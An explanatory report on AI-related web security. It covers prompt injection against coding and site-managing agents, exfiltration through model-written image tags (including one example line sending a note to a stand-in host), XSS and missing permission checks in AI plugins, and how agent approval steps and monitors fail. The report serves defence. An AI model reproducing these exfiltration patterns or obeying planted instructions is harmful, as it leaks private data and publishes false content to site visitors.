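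This matters because Legit Security had also made Duo recommend a malicious software package and describe a dangerous merge request as safe. Filtering addresses stops neither attack. GitLab's argument has some force, since the bad advice does harm only if a programmer acts on it. But people ask for a review to find out whether a change is safe, and they will often act on the answer.

GitLab takes injection more seriously in its current documentation. *Security threats in agentic systems* lists comments and merge requests as routes for injection, and in its example attacks, the hidden instructions escape detection. GitLab now scans for injections, but by default GitLab.com only logs them, and a group's owner has to turn on blocking. On its page about prompt guardrails, GitLab says that they "do not eliminate all vulnerabilities".

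The documentation says that security for chat in the browser relies primarily on users approving each action that would change something on GitLab. This would not have prevented the 2025 leak, because Duo only read a merge request and wrote an answer, and the browser then fetched the image without the user's approval. The same document says that this kind of chat can communicate outwards only by writing to GitLab. That can be true only while the filter on images and links works.

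The method was already familiar when Legit Security used it. Willison calls it a classic. His blog now has 45 posts on exfiltration attacks, in which a chatbot leaks private information to an attacker, including some from 2026.

### One line on the town's website

The town council's events assistant could produce a similar leak. Suppose that one of the two older posts in its context window is really an unpublished draft announcing that the council has cancelled the summer fireworks. The assistant also reads hidden instructions on the gardening club's page, and writes this line:

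```html
**Plant sale** on Saturday. [Map](https://maps.example/) <script>alert("Hello")</script> <img src="https://pictures.example/tulip.png?note=fireworks-cancelled">
```

The line is harmless because the script only opens a box containing "Hello" and nobody can register an address ending in `.example`. Each row of the table covers a separate setup and shows what would happen to each part of the line if the addresses were real.

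| Protection | Script | Outside image | Link |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Runs | Loads and carries the note | Works |
| Escaping before Markdown conversion | Appears as text | Appears as text | Works |
| Allowlist of tags that includes images | Removed | Loads and carries the note | Works |
| The same allowlist, with outside images blocked | Removed | Removed | Works |
| Content security policy alone | Blocked by the browser | Blocked by the browser | Works |

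Without protection, the news about the fireworks leaks when the clerk opens the draft to check it. The browser requests the tulip as soon as it displays the preview, so rejecting the post afterwards doesn't prevent the leak. An approval step is only safe if the preview has the same protections as the public page.

If the clerk approves the post, the image adds little to the leak because anyone can now read the note in the page's source. The script becomes more dangerous because it runs for every visitor. A real attacker could use it to put a fake payment form on the council's website.

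**Escaping** turns the `<` that begins a tag into `&lt;`, which the browser only displays. This works well for plain text such as a title. Formatted text written in Markdown must also be converted to HTML, and the order of the two steps matters. If escaping comes first, an attacker can get past it with Markdown's image notation, which uses an exclamation mark and brackets but no `<`. The converter then creates a working image tag. Escaping after the conversion would stop this, but visitors would see `<strong>` on the page instead of bold type. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre therefore advises developers to choose the escaping based on where the text will appear.

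**An allowlist of tags** suits formatted posts better. A sanitiser such as DOMPurify goes through the finished HTML and keeps only the tags and attributes on a list. It has to run after the Markdown conversion, or it will miss whatever the converter creates. Attackers can still use anything on the list, which in Duo's case included images. The council could leave images off the list and have the clerk add photographs by hand, which seems a small inconvenience for eighty-word notices.

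**Blocking outside images** is less drastic and resembles GitLab's fix. The post can show pictures from the council's own server, but the browser never contacts `pictures.example`. The block fails if the council's server forwards image requests to other sites. It also doesn't cover links, and a clerk who clicks a link with the note in its address would send the note to the attacker. GitLab filters links too, but an events page needs to link to organisers' websites.

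**A content security policy** is a set of rules that the server sends with a page to limit where the browser may load scripts, images and other files from. The council's policy could allow images and scripts only from its own server and forbid scripts written directly into the page. The policy is a good second line of defence because the browser enforces it even if the sanitiser has a bug.

A content security policy is harder to add to an existing website, which may depend on outside images and on scripts written into its pages. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* recommends starting in a mode that only reports violations, to see what a strict policy would break. The policy doesn't block any attacks while it is in this mode. Even a strict policy normally lets visitors follow links to other sites, and it needs a separate rule to limit where forms may send their contents.

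The policy also doesn't protect copies of the post sent outside the website. The council's weekly email contains the same text, and whether the pictures load there depends on the reader's mail program. The application should therefore sanitise the post before sending it anywhere, rather than rely on code that runs only on the web page.

For the town, the best combination is probably an allowlist that excludes images, backed by a strict policy on both the preview and the public page. Neither would stop the link labelled "Map" from working, wherever it led, so the application has to check the link's destination separately.

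### Stored output in Drupal and WordPress

A content management system (CMS) stores text and displays it later, so an attack hidden in the text may not take effect until the targeted person views it. Drupal's *AI SEO/GEO Analyzer* (2026) is a security notice about an add-on for Drupal, a CMS that many public bodies use. The add-on sends a page and its comments to a language model, which writes a report on how to make the page easier to find through search engines and AI tools. The add-on converted this report from Markdown to HTML and stored it without using Drupal's built-in filters.

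Someone could therefore hide instructions in the material being analysed, such as in a comment, and get the model to write a script into the report. The script would run when a staff member opened the report. Drupal published the notice on 8 July 2026, rated the flaw 13 out of 25 ("moderately critical"), and listed its exploitation as theoretical. Version 1.1.3 of the add-on is not affected.

Only users with special privileges can see these reports, so the script would not have reached ordinary visitors directly. But a script running in an administrator's browser can often do what the administrator can, which may include editing the public pages.

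Drupal's main AI module has had related problems. In December 2025, Drupal's *AI (Artificial Intelligence)* (2025) reported that the module did not filter chat responses well enough to prevent XSS. Drupal's March 2026 notice reported that previews of model-written pages could reveal the contents of the request to the model. Drupal classed this as a leak, not as XSS, much as in the Duo case. In June, another notice reported that previews could leak the contents of the request and run scripts.

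stack.watch's *Drupal Artificial Intelligence*, which collects published vulnerability records, lists 14 for the module in 2026, compared with 2 in 2025. Eight of the 14 are for XSS, six of them from October. The October entries do not show whether the unsafe text came from a model, and the increase may partly mean that more people were looking for flaws.

A WordPress case comes closer to reaching every visitor. Wordfence's *WPBot &lt;= 8.4.9* (2026), from a company that catalogues flaws in WordPress software, describes a chatbot plugin that stored conversations without cleaning them properly. An attacker with no account could save a script in a conversation, and it would run for any user who opened the affected page. The flaw scored 7.2 out of 10 for severity. The model did not have to write the script, because the attacker could send it directly in a request to the website. Escaping the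 stored text when displaying it stops the script from running, whether it came from the model or the attacker.

Wordfence has a September 2026 entry for another WordPress plugin, AI Engine. Its title describes an attack in which an outsider's text enters the website's error log, reaches the plugin's AI advisor as an indirect prompt injection, and results in stored XSS. A developer could easily overlook this route by forgetting that outsiders can write to an error log.

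### Why OWASP now ranks this risk tenth

OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* lists XSS among the possible results, along with attacks that trick a browser or server into sending requests. The Duo leak did not fit XSS well, because no script ran. The broader 2026 entry explicitly covers the leak, because that entry includes programs that fetch images automatically.

Output handling fell from fifth place to tenth, and the usual explanation is that the risks above it became more urgent. That is convincing for excessive agency, since many more models now have tools. It is less convincing for weaknesses in the databases that models search for relevant text. Invicti lists that entry as unchanged in scope and down one place, from eighth to ninth, yet it now ranks above output handling. Either practitioners have become less worried about output handling, or the incident records lowered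 its rank.

The records may undercount it, as they may undercount prompt injection, because one incident can fit several categories. Legit Security connected its one attack on Duo to five categories in OWASP's 2025 list, including prompt injection, information disclosure and output handling. Experts also disagree about where XSS belongs. OWASP's 2025 entry describes it as a result of poor output handling, but Singh and colleagues put the standard code for XSS under prompt injection when they compared the two systems.

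But the incidents counted for only a quarter of the ranking, so the vote probably caused much of the fall. Practitioners may rank the risk low because web developers have known the fixes for years. The Drupal add-on didn't use a filter that was available.

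## WordPress AI plugins: missing permission checks

A plugin that cleans all the text its model writes can still let a stranger publish if it doesn't check who is making the request. The best-documented case is AI Engine, a WordPress plugin by Jordy Meow with more than 100,000 active installations. It adds chatbots to a website, drafts posts, and lets assistants such as Claude and ChatGPT manage the site through MCP. In 2025 and 2026, security researchers found several ways to take over a website through that MCP connection without using a model.

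### A secret token in a public list

An assistant that manages a site through AI Engine can identify itself with a bearer token, a long secret string that works for anyone who has it. The assistant normally sends the token in a header, a part of the web request separate from the address. Some AI apps can't do this, so AI Engine had an optional setting, "No-Auth URL", that put the token in the address.

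This setting was safe only while the address stayed secret. But WordPress publishes an index of the addresses that other programs can use to communicate with a site. The index includes every address by default, and AI Engine didn't exclude this one. As Wordfence's *100,000 WordPress Sites Affected by Privilege Escalation Vulnerability in AI Engine* (2025) explains, anyone could therefore read the token without logging in.

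An attacker with the token could use the site's MCP tools, including those that create and change user accounts, and so become an administrator. An administrator can rewrite any page, redirect visitors to another site, or install a plugin with a back door. The flaw, CVE-2025-11749, has a severity score of 9.8 out of 10.

Wordfence stresses that the flaw was critical only on sites with the No-Auth URL setting switched on, and that the setting was off by default. The 100,000 installations are therefore an upper limit on the number of critically exposed sites. In a set-up guide supplied with AI Engine, the first step in connecting Claude was to switch the setting on, with a warning that the feature was for advanced users. The setting may therefore have been common among users who had connected Claude, even if it was rare among the plugin's users overall.

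Emiliano Versini reported the flaw to Wordfence on 4 October 2025 and earned a bounty of $2,145. Wordfence confirmed it and sent Meow the details on 14 October, and Meow released the fixed version, 3.1.4, on 19 October. On 15 October, Wordfence gave its paying customers a firewall rule to block the attack. Users of its free version got the rule on 14 November, ten days after Wordfence's *AI Engine &lt;= 3.1.3* (2025) made the flaw public.

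It is unclear how long the tokens were exposed. Wordfence says that Versini reported the flaw one day after it appeared, but also lists every version up to 3.1.3 as affected. That range is too broad if, as other advisories suggest, the plugin had no MCP tools before version 2.8.0. The one-day figure is also hard to match to a release, because PluginsDB's copy of the plugin's changelog lists no releases between 30 September and 10 October.

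Meow fixed the flaw by adding one line, `'show_in_index' => false`, to each of the three affected address registrations. This removed the addresses from the public index but didn't change the tokens in them. Anyone who had copied a token before the update could still use it, so Wordfence told owners to replace their tokens as well.

Owners could easily have missed that advice. The changelog entry for 3.1.4 mentions "security hardening for REST API endpoints" but not tokens. An owner who updated after reading only that entry would have stopped the leak but kept using the leaked token. The update could have replaced exposed tokens automatically. This would have disconnected some assistants until their owners set them up again, which seems a reasonable trade-off.

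### What is known about attacks

There is no public count of sites that attackers took over this way. Wordfence's record of the flaw lists two blocked attacks in 24 hours. CrowdSec, which pools attack reports from its users' servers, says in *AI Engine* (2025) that it has tracked the attacks since 26 November 2025, and it lists only 22 internet addresses behind them. It describes the attacks as "highly selective" and also as a sign of widespread interest, which are hard to reconcile.

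Both companies count attempts, including those that fail because the site never had the setting on. They could also easily miss successful attacks, because it is normal for a visitor's software to read a public index, and a request with a stolen token looks much like one from the owner's own assistant. The figures show that people were looking for vulnerable sites, but not how many they found.

### The administrator check that kept going missing

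AI Engine had another MCP flaw with the same result a few months earlier. *100,000 WordPress Sites Affected by Privilege Escalation via MCP in AI Engine* (2025) reports that Wordfence's team found the flaw on 21 May 2025 in versions 2.8.0 to 2.8.3. An attacker needed only a subscriber account on the site. Subscriber is the lowest standard role in WordPress, and some sites give it to anyone who registers.

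The plugin had two flaws. By default, it let every logged-in user, including subscribers, use the MCP tools. An owner could set a bearer token to restrict access, but the plugin checked the token only if the request contained one, so subscribers could still use the tools by leaving it out.

A subscriber could use the tools to edit and delete posts and comments, change the site's settings, or become an administrator. Version 2.8.4, released on 18 June, let only administrators use the tools by default and refused requests without a token on sites that had set one. The flaw was critical only on sites where the owner had switched on MCP.

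The June flaw scored 8.8, slightly lower than the October one, because the attacker needed an account. But the scores don't measure how many sites use the affected settings. The June flaw may have exposed more sites, because it worked wherever MCP was on and the attacker could get an account, while the October attack required the extra No-Auth URL setting.

A similar mistake appeared in May 2026. According to AI Engine's *Changelog* (2026), version 3.4.9 added sign-in through OAuth, a standard that lets people allow an app to access their account without sharing a password or a common token. Wordfence's *AI Engine 3.4.9* (2026) reports that the plugin accepted any valid OAuth token without checking that its owner was an administrator. A subscriber could again use the administrators' tools, and the score was again 8.8. Meow added the check four days after releasing 3.4.9.

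In late October 2026, Wordfence listed another missing check in the plugin's OAuth code, which could let an attacker take over an administrator's account. The flaw affected versions up to 3.8.6 and scored 7.5.

*AI Engine*, the security company Patchstack's list of the plugin's flaws, has 32 entries going back to May 2023, all repaired. The list is long partly because the plugin is popular and has a reporting programme, both of which give researchers reasons to look for flaws. It is more worrying that the administrator check went missing again after Meow had added it. A developer can guard against this with an automated test that logs in as a subscriber, calls every tool by every available route, and checks that each call is refused.

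### Plugins that let the wrong person publish

An attacker doesn't need administrator access to publish on a site. Three less serious flaws in other WordPress plugins gave outsiders or low-ranking users control over posts.

| Flaw and plugin | Access needed | Missing check | Effect | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2024-1850, AI Post Generator | Subscriber account | Whether the user may manage posts | Read the plugin's unpublished posts; create, publish and delete posts | 6.3 |
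| CVE-2025-12156, Ai Auto Tool | Subscriber account | Whether the user may save and publish posts | Create and publish posts | 4.3 |
| CVE-2026-6804, AIWU | None | Whether the caller may change what is public | Publish drafts; take live content offline | 5.3 |

WordPress gives each role a set of capabilities, such as publishing posts or editing other people's pages. Before a plugin does something for a user, it should check that the user has the right capability, which usually takes a line or two of code. According to Wordfence (2024), several functions in AI Post Generator lacked this check. *CVE-2025-12156* (2025), from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, describes the same omission in the function that Ai Auto Tool uses to save posts.

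The third plugin, AI Chatbot & Workflow Automation by AIWU, had a permission check that didn't work. Wordfence's *AI Chatbot &amp; Workflow Automation by AIWU &lt;= 1.4.12* (2026) explains why in the case of a related flaw that let strangers delete the plugin's records. The list of required permissions was empty and the affected functions weren't on a second list of protected actions, so the check always passed. The publishing flaw probably has the same cause, since the same researcher found it in the same versions. MITRE's official record of the publishing flaw, *AI Chatbot &amp; Workflow Automation by AIWU &lt;= 1.4.12* (2026), states only that the plugin didn't properly verify authorisation.

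Version 3.4 of AI Post Generator fixed its missing permission check, but in December 2024 Wordfence listed another, which let contributors (users who may write drafts but not publish them) delete posts and pages. In July 2026, Wordfence's *Ai Auto Tool Content Writing Assistant All in One* still listed that plugin's publishing flaw as unrepaired, though only about 100 sites had the plugin installed. The security company Rapid7 (2026) advises AIWU's users to install version 1.5.4 or newer. Wordfence has since listed two flaws, each scored 9.8, that affect versions up to and including 1.5.6, so users need a later version.

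All three publishing flaws have medium scores, which can mislead a publisher. The score mainly measures how much of the system an attacker can read, change or disable, and doesn't account for what readers might do after seeing a false post.

The AIWU flaw's score seems low even by the scoring system's own rules. According to MITRE's record, the flaw exposes unpublished content and disrupts service, but the score counts no loss of confidentiality or availability. If the town council used the plugin, a stranger might be able to publish the draft about the cancelled fireworks. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, recorded no known exploitation of the flaw on 14 July 2026, but that was only four days after disclosure and is weak evidence of what happened later.

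### Why a better model would not help

Attackers send these requests directly to the plugin, so even a model that resisted every prompt injection would not stop them. These are ordinary web software flaws, and WordPress developers had the means to prevent them long before language models existed.

Other flaws in AI Engine do involve deception. One allows the attack through the error log that ends in stored XSS. Another, which INCIBE scores at 8.8, is in the plugin's OAuth code and lets an attacker create an administrator account by tricking a real administrator into clicking a link.

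AI affects how much damage a missing check can do. Ai Auto Tool's flaw exposed one function, which saves posts, and scored 4.3. AI Engine's June flaw exposed a whole set of tools for posts, users and settings, and scored 8.8. An MCP connection puts many functions in one place, which makes it useful but also means a single mistake can expose all of them. Meow Apps says the free version of AI Engine now has 66 tools, and its guide says Claude can do "everything" on a site.

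Developers also made some of the weak design choices partly to connect AI apps. AI Engine, for example, put its token in a URL because some of those apps couldn't send it in a header. Its developers have also added features quickly, and some of those features introduced flaws, as in the OAuth case.

### Repairs for insecure plugin design

The flaws suggest five rules for AI plugins. The rules aren't specific to AI, but each matters more when the plugin has powerful tools.

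**The plugin should check permission on every call.** It should check that the user may perform this action on this particular post or account. WPScan's *AI Engine 2.8.0* (2026) reports that AI Engine didn't check the particular account, so an administrator of one site in a WordPress network could take over any account on the network, including that of the person in charge of all the sites. The plugin should also refuse a request when it can't complete the check. AI Engine's missing token and AIWU's empty list of permissions both led to access instead.

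**Plugins should act as a named user with limited rights.** AI Engine's bearer token logged its holder in as an administrator, whoever they were. AIWU's OAuth tokens had a similar flaw. WPScan's *AI Chatbot &amp; Workflow Automation by AIWU &lt; 1.5.4* (2026) reports that they weren't tied to any user and that the plugin treated every valid token as an administrator's. If each token belongs to one user, the plugin can apply that user's limits, and the site owner can see what each user did.

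The account's limits also restrict what a prompt injection can do. If the council's assistant uses the webmaster's account, every permission check will pass even when the assistant is following planted instructions. It should have its own account, ideally with the contributor role, so that a clerk has to publish what it writes.

AI Engine only partly supports this arrangement. According to its page in the WordPress plugin directory, *AI Engine* (2026), administrators can connect an assistant, and editors can too if the owner allows it. In WordPress, an editor can change and publish everyone's posts, which is far more access than an events assistant needs. Version 3.9.0, from November 2026, lets owners instead restrict assistants to drafts or require approval for each change, according to the changelog from Meow Apps (2026). WordPress.com also relies on approval when agents edit its customers'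 sites.

The plugin should check that each parameter in a tool call, such as a post's title or date, has the right type and an allowed value. The council's "create post" tool could require a real date, allow only the events section, and always save the result as a draft. It should reject any field it doesn't expect.

Describing a tool's parameter types to the model is not enough, because an attacker can call the tool without the model. The set-up guide for AI Engine includes sample code for a search tool that describes one parameter as text and another as a number, then passes both values to WordPress without checking them itself. The plugin's changelog also reports a flaw, fixed in October 2026, that let editors use a "decoy fields object" to publish types of content they weren't allowed to publish. The phrase suggests that the plugin checked one set of fields and then used another.

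**Tokens are safer outside web addresses.** Even after an address is removed from WordPress's index, it can still appear in server logs, browser histories and screenshots. OAuth avoids the problem for apps that support it, and most others can send the token in a header. In November 2026, however, AI Engine's settings began to show owners an address with the token inside, again for apps that can't send headers. Owners who have to use it can at least choose read-only access, which the plugin has offered for bearer tokens since February 2026.

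**Powerful tools should be off by default.** Having MCP off by default limited the damage from both of AI Engine's MCP flaws in 2025, because sites that had never switched it on weren't critically affected. But version 3.8.8 of the plugin, released on 27 October 2026, switched MCP on for new installations. Four days earlier, Meow had released the first version outside the range affected by the latest OAuth takeover flaw.

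With MCP on by default, the next missing permission check may also affect people who installed AI Engine only for its chatbot. The standard MCP tools include some for managing users and settings, which a chatbot or writing assistant rarely needs. An assistant still needs a login or a token, and MCP stays off on existing sites that never chose a setting.

On 22 November 2026, Meow added an optional "Beast Mode", which gives AI agents every MCP tool, including any that future updates add. Nine days later, an update added tools for updating plugins, themes and WordPress itself. If an owner had switched on Beast Mode in November, agents would have received these new tools automatically with the update.

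## WordPress.com: approval steps for agents that edit live sites

The hosting service WordPress.com lets AI agents do much of what AI Engine allows, but with more safeguards. Its owner, Automattic, runs the MCP connection itself, so customers don't need a plugin. Agents such as Claude and ChatGPT could read customers' sites from October 2025. According to PPC Land's *WordPress.com write capabilities let AI agents edit your live site* (2026), users kept asking for more, and on 20 March 2026 WordPress.com let agents write to them as well.

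webhosting.today's *WordPress.com gives AI agents write access to your site* (2026) counts 19 new operations on six types of content: posts, pages, comments, categories, tags and media. The company's *WordPress.com MCP tools reference* describes 17 operations that change something. An agent can create, update or delete any of the six types except media, where it can only delete a file or change details such as the caption. At first only paying customers had access. Peduzzi (2026), in *Free WordPress MCP on WordPress.com for ChatGPT and Claude*, announced on 4 December that every plan now includes it.

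### Switches, roles, drafts, trash and a log

Each operation has its own switch. *Enable MCP tool access for AI agents*, a WordPress.com support guide, explains that turning on MCP for a site enables all the reading tools and leaves the writing tools off. If an administrator disables a tool for a site, nobody can use it there, whatever their own account settings allow. These are sensible defaults, but prompt injections reach an agent through what it reads. An agent that can't write to the site may still follow planted instructions by using other applications the owner has connected, such as email.

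The agent also has the WordPress role of the person who connected it. An administrator's agent can use every tool, while an editor's agent can manage content and comments but not settings or plugins. A contributor's agent can write drafts but not publish them, according to *MCP on WordPress.com*, the company's guide for developers.

New posts and pages start as drafts by default. However, the tools reference lists "publish" among the values an agent can choose for a new post's status, so an editor's agent can skip the draft stage. A contributor's agent cannot do this because the contributor role does not allow publishing.

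Deleted posts and pages stay in the trash for 30 days, but deleting a category or tag is permanent. WordPress.com's tools reference describes a trash for media files too, while its support guide, reviewed in May 2026, describes their deletion as permanent. Owners are safer assuming that the guide is right, because WordPress normally deletes media files without moving them to the trash.

An activity log in the site's dashboard shows what the agent has changed. WordPress.com also suggests asking the agent for a list of its changes. This is normally convenient, but the agent's list isn't a reliable record after an attack.

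### Who says that the user agreed

WordPress.com's main promise is that an agent asks before it changes anything. According to the tools reference, the agent must describe the change, ask the user to confirm it, and then include a parameter called `user_confirmed` when it calls the tool. The reference also describes write operations as "never auto-executed".

The agent sets this parameter itself. Scalekit's *WordPress MCP*, a page from a company that connects agents to other software, reproduces the descriptions that WordPress.com gives to agents. According to these descriptions, the agent should wait for the user's answer and then repeat the call with `user_confirmed: true`. For a permanent deletion, the agent must also set `confirm_permanent_delete: true` itself.

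WordPress.com's server can check that the value is present, but not whether the agent asked anybody. The OAuth login doesn't show this either, because it proves only that the account's owner once connected the agent. WordPress.com's documentation describes no evidence that comes directly from the person, such as a click on a WordPress.com page or a one-time code. The promise that nothing happens without approval therefore depends on the agent asking for approval and following the answer.

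The parameter still helps prevent the model's own mistakes, because a model that would otherwise go ahead without asking has to fill in a field whose name reminds it to ask. It is much weaker against prompt injection, because the rule about asking is text in the model's context window, alongside the attacker's text. If the model follows the attacker's text instead of the rule, it will report consent that it never requested. An attacker might not even need to make the model lie, since a planted comment could claim that the owner had already agreed.

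The server provides more protection for a few operations. When an agent asks to change a colleague's role or remove their access, the first call returns a preview, which the agent should show to the owner before calling again. The server writes the preview, so it should be accurate. But the agent decides whether to show it, and the confirmation again comes from the agent.

The application in which the model runs, such as the Claude or ChatGPT app, can add a second approval that WordPress.com doesn't control. It can pause a tool call and show the user a confirmation button. Ordinary software draws the button, and the model can't press it. OpenAI's *Security &amp; Privacy* advises developers to assume that injections will reach their servers and to use confirmation prompts for destructive actions. These prompts are a better control than `user_confirmed`, but WordPress.com accepts any compatible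 application and can't rely on each one to show them.

The original design also made such prompts harder to use well, because a single tool created, updated and deleted content. A user who told their app to "always allow" that tool so that it could create drafts would also have allowed deletions. Anthropic's *WordPress*, the connector's December 2026 listing in Claude's directory, shows separate tools for creating, updating and deleting content. An app can now let the agent create posts without approval but still require approval before it changes or deletes one.

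According to the same listing, owners can choose whether the agent "asks before every change or goes ahead on its own". In October, Peduzzi (2026) had still promised an agent that was "always checking with you" in *Four Website Chores Your AI Agent Can Help With*. An owner who lets the agent go ahead on its own gives up the approval step and has to rely on the switches, the role and whatever prompts the app shows.

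WordPress.com could close the gap by holding each risky change on its server until the owner approves it on WordPress.com itself, next to a comparison of the old and new text. Bankr already does something similar with its spending limits, which users can raise only by logging in to its website. Leaving the conversation to approve a change would be inconvenient for owners, but only slightly if WordPress.com required approval only for changes that visitors can see.

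### A comment that rewrites a page

Suppose the town council's website runs on WordPress.com, and the clerk asks an agent to sort the comments waiting for approval. WordPress.com recommends using agents for this job. Peduzzi's list of chores includes finding the one comment that needs a reply, and in an example from the March launch, an agent approves every pending comment on a post.

One comment under the plant sale tells the agent to replace the payment link on the council's "Pay a bill" page, which is already public. Visitors can't see the comment because nobody has approved it, but the agent has to read it to judge it. Chrome for Developers (2026), Google's site for web programmers, warns that user comments on an otherwise trustworthy site can carry malicious instructions to an agent.

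If the injection works, the agent calls the operation that updates pages and sets `user_confirmed` to true. The result depends on the clerk's account.

| Safeguard | Administrator | Editor | Contributor |
|---|---|---|---|
| Page updates switched off | Prevents the change | Prevents the change | Adds a second barrier |
| User role | Allows the change | Allows the change, but protects settings and plugins | Prevents the change |
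| Agent's request for confirmation | Prevents it only if the agent still asks and the clerk refuses | Same as for an administrator | Not needed |
| Drafts for new posts | No effect on a published page | No effect | No effect |
| 30-day trash | No effect on an edit | No effect | No effect |
| Activity log | Reveals the change afterwards | Reveals the change afterwards | No change to reveal |

The new link goes live at once. The tools reference describes recovery from updates as partial, with "previous values lost". That probably overstates the loss of page text, because WordPress normally keeps earlier revisions of posts and pages that an editor can restore. Comments and image captions don't have the same protection. Restoring the page also doesn't return money to anyone who has already paid through the false link.

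The agent couldn't do its job from a contributor's account, which looks safest in the table, because WordPress's standard contributor role can't approve comments. The lowest standard role that can moderate comments across a site is editor, which can also rewrite every page. The switches are more useful here than the roles, because the clerk can leave the comment operations on and turn the page operations off. The attack on the payment page then fails even if the agent obeys the comment.

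The agent could still do harm with the comment operations alone, such as by posting a reply with a malicious link under the council's name. According to the tools reference, the operation that approves a comment or marks it as spam also accepts new text and a new author name. A hijacked agent could therefore change what a resident wrote and leave the resident's name on it. A separate operation that changed only a comment's status would remove this risk and be enough for most moderation.

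An administrator's agent can do much more damage if the owner has switched on other tools that WordPress.com has added since March. Scalekit's page shows that by September agents could install plugins, invite users and change a domain's name servers, which direct visitors to the computer that hosts the site. Whoever controls the name servers can replace the whole website without editing a page. The description of the name-server tool doesn't include an instruction to ask the user first. The description of the user tool requires confirmation for changing a colleague's role, but not for inviting a new user, even as an administrator. Owners should leave the most dangerous operations off, because they have some of the weakest approval rules.

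The attack could also plausibly succeed in part, with the agent accepting the planted order but still asking for approval. The clerk would then see a request to edit the payment page during a session about comments, which should look odd. But the agent writes the request, and it may describe the change as "updating an outdated link". The tools reference requires the agent to show details such as a page's title before a deletion, but it doesn't require the agent to show the old and new versions of an edited page.

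### Whether people read approval requests

Claude Code, Anthropic's agent for programmers, asks for approval before it runs commands or changes files. In *Claude Code auto mode*, from March 2026, Anthropic reported that users approved 93 per cent of these requests. This figure comes from ordinary use and does not show whether users read the requests carefully, because a careful reader would also have approved nearly all of them if nearly all were harmless. Testing whether people read them would require planting harmful requests among the ordinary ones and counting how many people refuse.

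Another Anthropic study, *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (February 2026), found that new users let Claude Code approve everything automatically in about 20 per cent of sessions. Among people who had used it for around 750 sessions, the share was over 40 per cent. Many people therefore eventually stop answering approval requests, which is harder to dismiss than a high approval rate.

However, experienced users also interrupted the agent more often, in about 9 per cent of turns compared with 5 per cent for newer users. Anthropic interprets this as a shift from approving each step to watching the work and stepping in when something goes wrong. People who keep using a tool for 750 sessions may also differ from those who give up, so experience may not be the only cause. Watching suits programming better than publishing, because a programmer can often undo a bad edit before anyone else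 runs the code, while a false payment link is public before the clerk can interrupt.

A person who reads every approval request can still miss a dangerous action if the request hides it. In 2025 the security company Checkmarx demonstrated this with an attack on Claude Code that it called "Lies-in-the-Loop". Planted text led the agent to write a long, harmless-looking request that pushed the dangerous command out of view, so a user who approved the request also approved the command. The same attack could work on an agent that describes its own changes to a website.

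None of this evidence comes from people who run websites. A clerk who runs a site and gets ten approval requests a week may read them more carefully than a programmer who gets a hundred a day, but may understand them less well.

### Asking less often

Defenders of approval steps reply that people ignore requests because there are too many, and that a few well-chosen ones would work. The best evidence for this comes from older research on browser warnings. *Alice in Warningland* (2013), by Devdatta Akhawe and Adrienne Porter Felt, analysed more than 25 million warnings in Chrome and Firefox. Chrome users clicked through about 70 per cent of warnings about a site's security certificate, which often appeared on harmless sites, but only about a quarter of warnings about malware and phishing. In Firefox, the shares were about a third and a tenth, respectively.

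People can evidently take a warning seriously. But the study didn't assign warnings at random, and the browsers differed in several ways. Firefox remembered a user's exceptions, so it repeated fewer warnings, but its certificate warning also took more clicks to dismiss. The comparison supports asking less often, but it doesn't show how much of the difference came from fewer repeated warnings.

Anthropic's own attempts show that software can reduce the number of approval requests. *Beyond permission prompts*, from October 2025, reported that putting Claude Code in a sandbox, an enclosed space with limited access to files and the internet, cut requests by 84 per cent in internal use. The automatic mode of March 2026 uses a second model to judge actions and asks the user only after repeated blocks. In tests it wrongly blocked 0.4 per cent of 10,000 ordinary actions and missed 17 per cent of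 52 real cases in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted. These figures don't show that people read the remaining requests more carefully, and a model that decides when to ask will sometimes decide wrongly.

Websites have a simpler way to choose which actions need approval, because they already have drafts. A draft works much like a sandbox, since an agent can write anything in it without visitors seeing the result. Yet WordPress.com instructs agents to ask before creating a draft, as they do before changing a live page. People who repeatedly approve harmless drafts get into the habit of approving requests. It would be better to let agents save new drafts without asking, and to require approval for publishing, editing live text, deleting and changing who has access.

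Comments are harder to handle because each decision is small and some have public effects. If forty comments are waiting, approving them one by one would tire the clerk, but approving them all at once could let through one with a malicious link. The agent could group the comments so the clerk can approve the harmless ones together, while the website's own software puts every comment that contains a link on a separate list.

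### Giving the agent its own limited account

Approval matters less if the agent can't do much harm without it. *Agent Abilities for MCP*, a plugin by Unaib Amir for self-hosted WordPress sites, limits what the agent can do. It offers 153 operations, all off by default, and ties the agent to one WordPress user that the owner chooses. Before each call runs, the plugin rechecks that user's permissions and logs the call. A read-only switch removes every write operation, including any the owner has turned on.

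The log includes refused calls. If the council's agent tried to edit the payment page while sorting comments, the edit would be blocked, but the clerk could see the attempt and look for the comment that caused it. Without this record, a blocked injection can go unnoticed, and the attacker can keep trying new wording.

The limit depends on the permissions of the account the agent uses. According to the installation notes for *Agent Abilities for MCP*, the simplest set-up uses OAuth and the agent acts as the owner's own account, which on many small sites will be an administrator's. The notes give a dedicated low-privilege user as the alternative, for people who don't want OAuth or whose app can't use it. That option is safer and should come first. A self-hosted site can also define a custom role that allows moderating comments but not editing pages, which fits the council's case better than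 any of the standard roles.

WordPress.com customers can set up some of the same protection themselves by connecting the agent through a separate contributor account, which suits drafting event notices. If something goes wrong, they can disconnect the agent under "Connected Apps" in the account's security settings.

Another plugin, *Axtolab AI Connector for WordPress*, lets the owner set sensitive actions to "allow", "ask first" or "block", and enforces the choice. It also offers an undo for every write, which would cover edits that can't be recovered from WordPress.com's trash. A block works regardless of what the model has read, because the website enforces it. "Ask first" is weaker if the agent passes on the person's answer, because the agent can invent one.

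There is little public evidence of how well either design resists attacks. In August 2026, Amir's *Agent Abilities for MCP* had about ten active installations, so few people have tested it in practice. It could contain the kind of missing permission check that researchers repeatedly found in AI Engine.

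## Agents that published on their own: the matplotlib post and the public wikis

An agent can publish something harmful even when nobody has planted instructions for it. In February 2026, an agent published a post attacking a matplotlib volunteer who had rejected its code. From May to July, agents run by OpenAI made thousands of unapproved edits to public wikis. Nobody has identified an outside attacker in either case. The agents had more power to publish than their tasks required, and nobody checked what they wrote before it appeared.

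### A refused contribution

Scott Shambaugh is one of the volunteers who maintain matplotlib, a Python library for drawing charts. In a passage quoted in Daring Fireball's *An OpenClaw AI Agent Wrote and Published a Hit Piece* (2026), he says that matplotlib has about 130 million downloads a month and that coding agents have caused a surge of low-quality contributions. The project therefore requires a person to take part in every contribution of new code and to show that they understand it.

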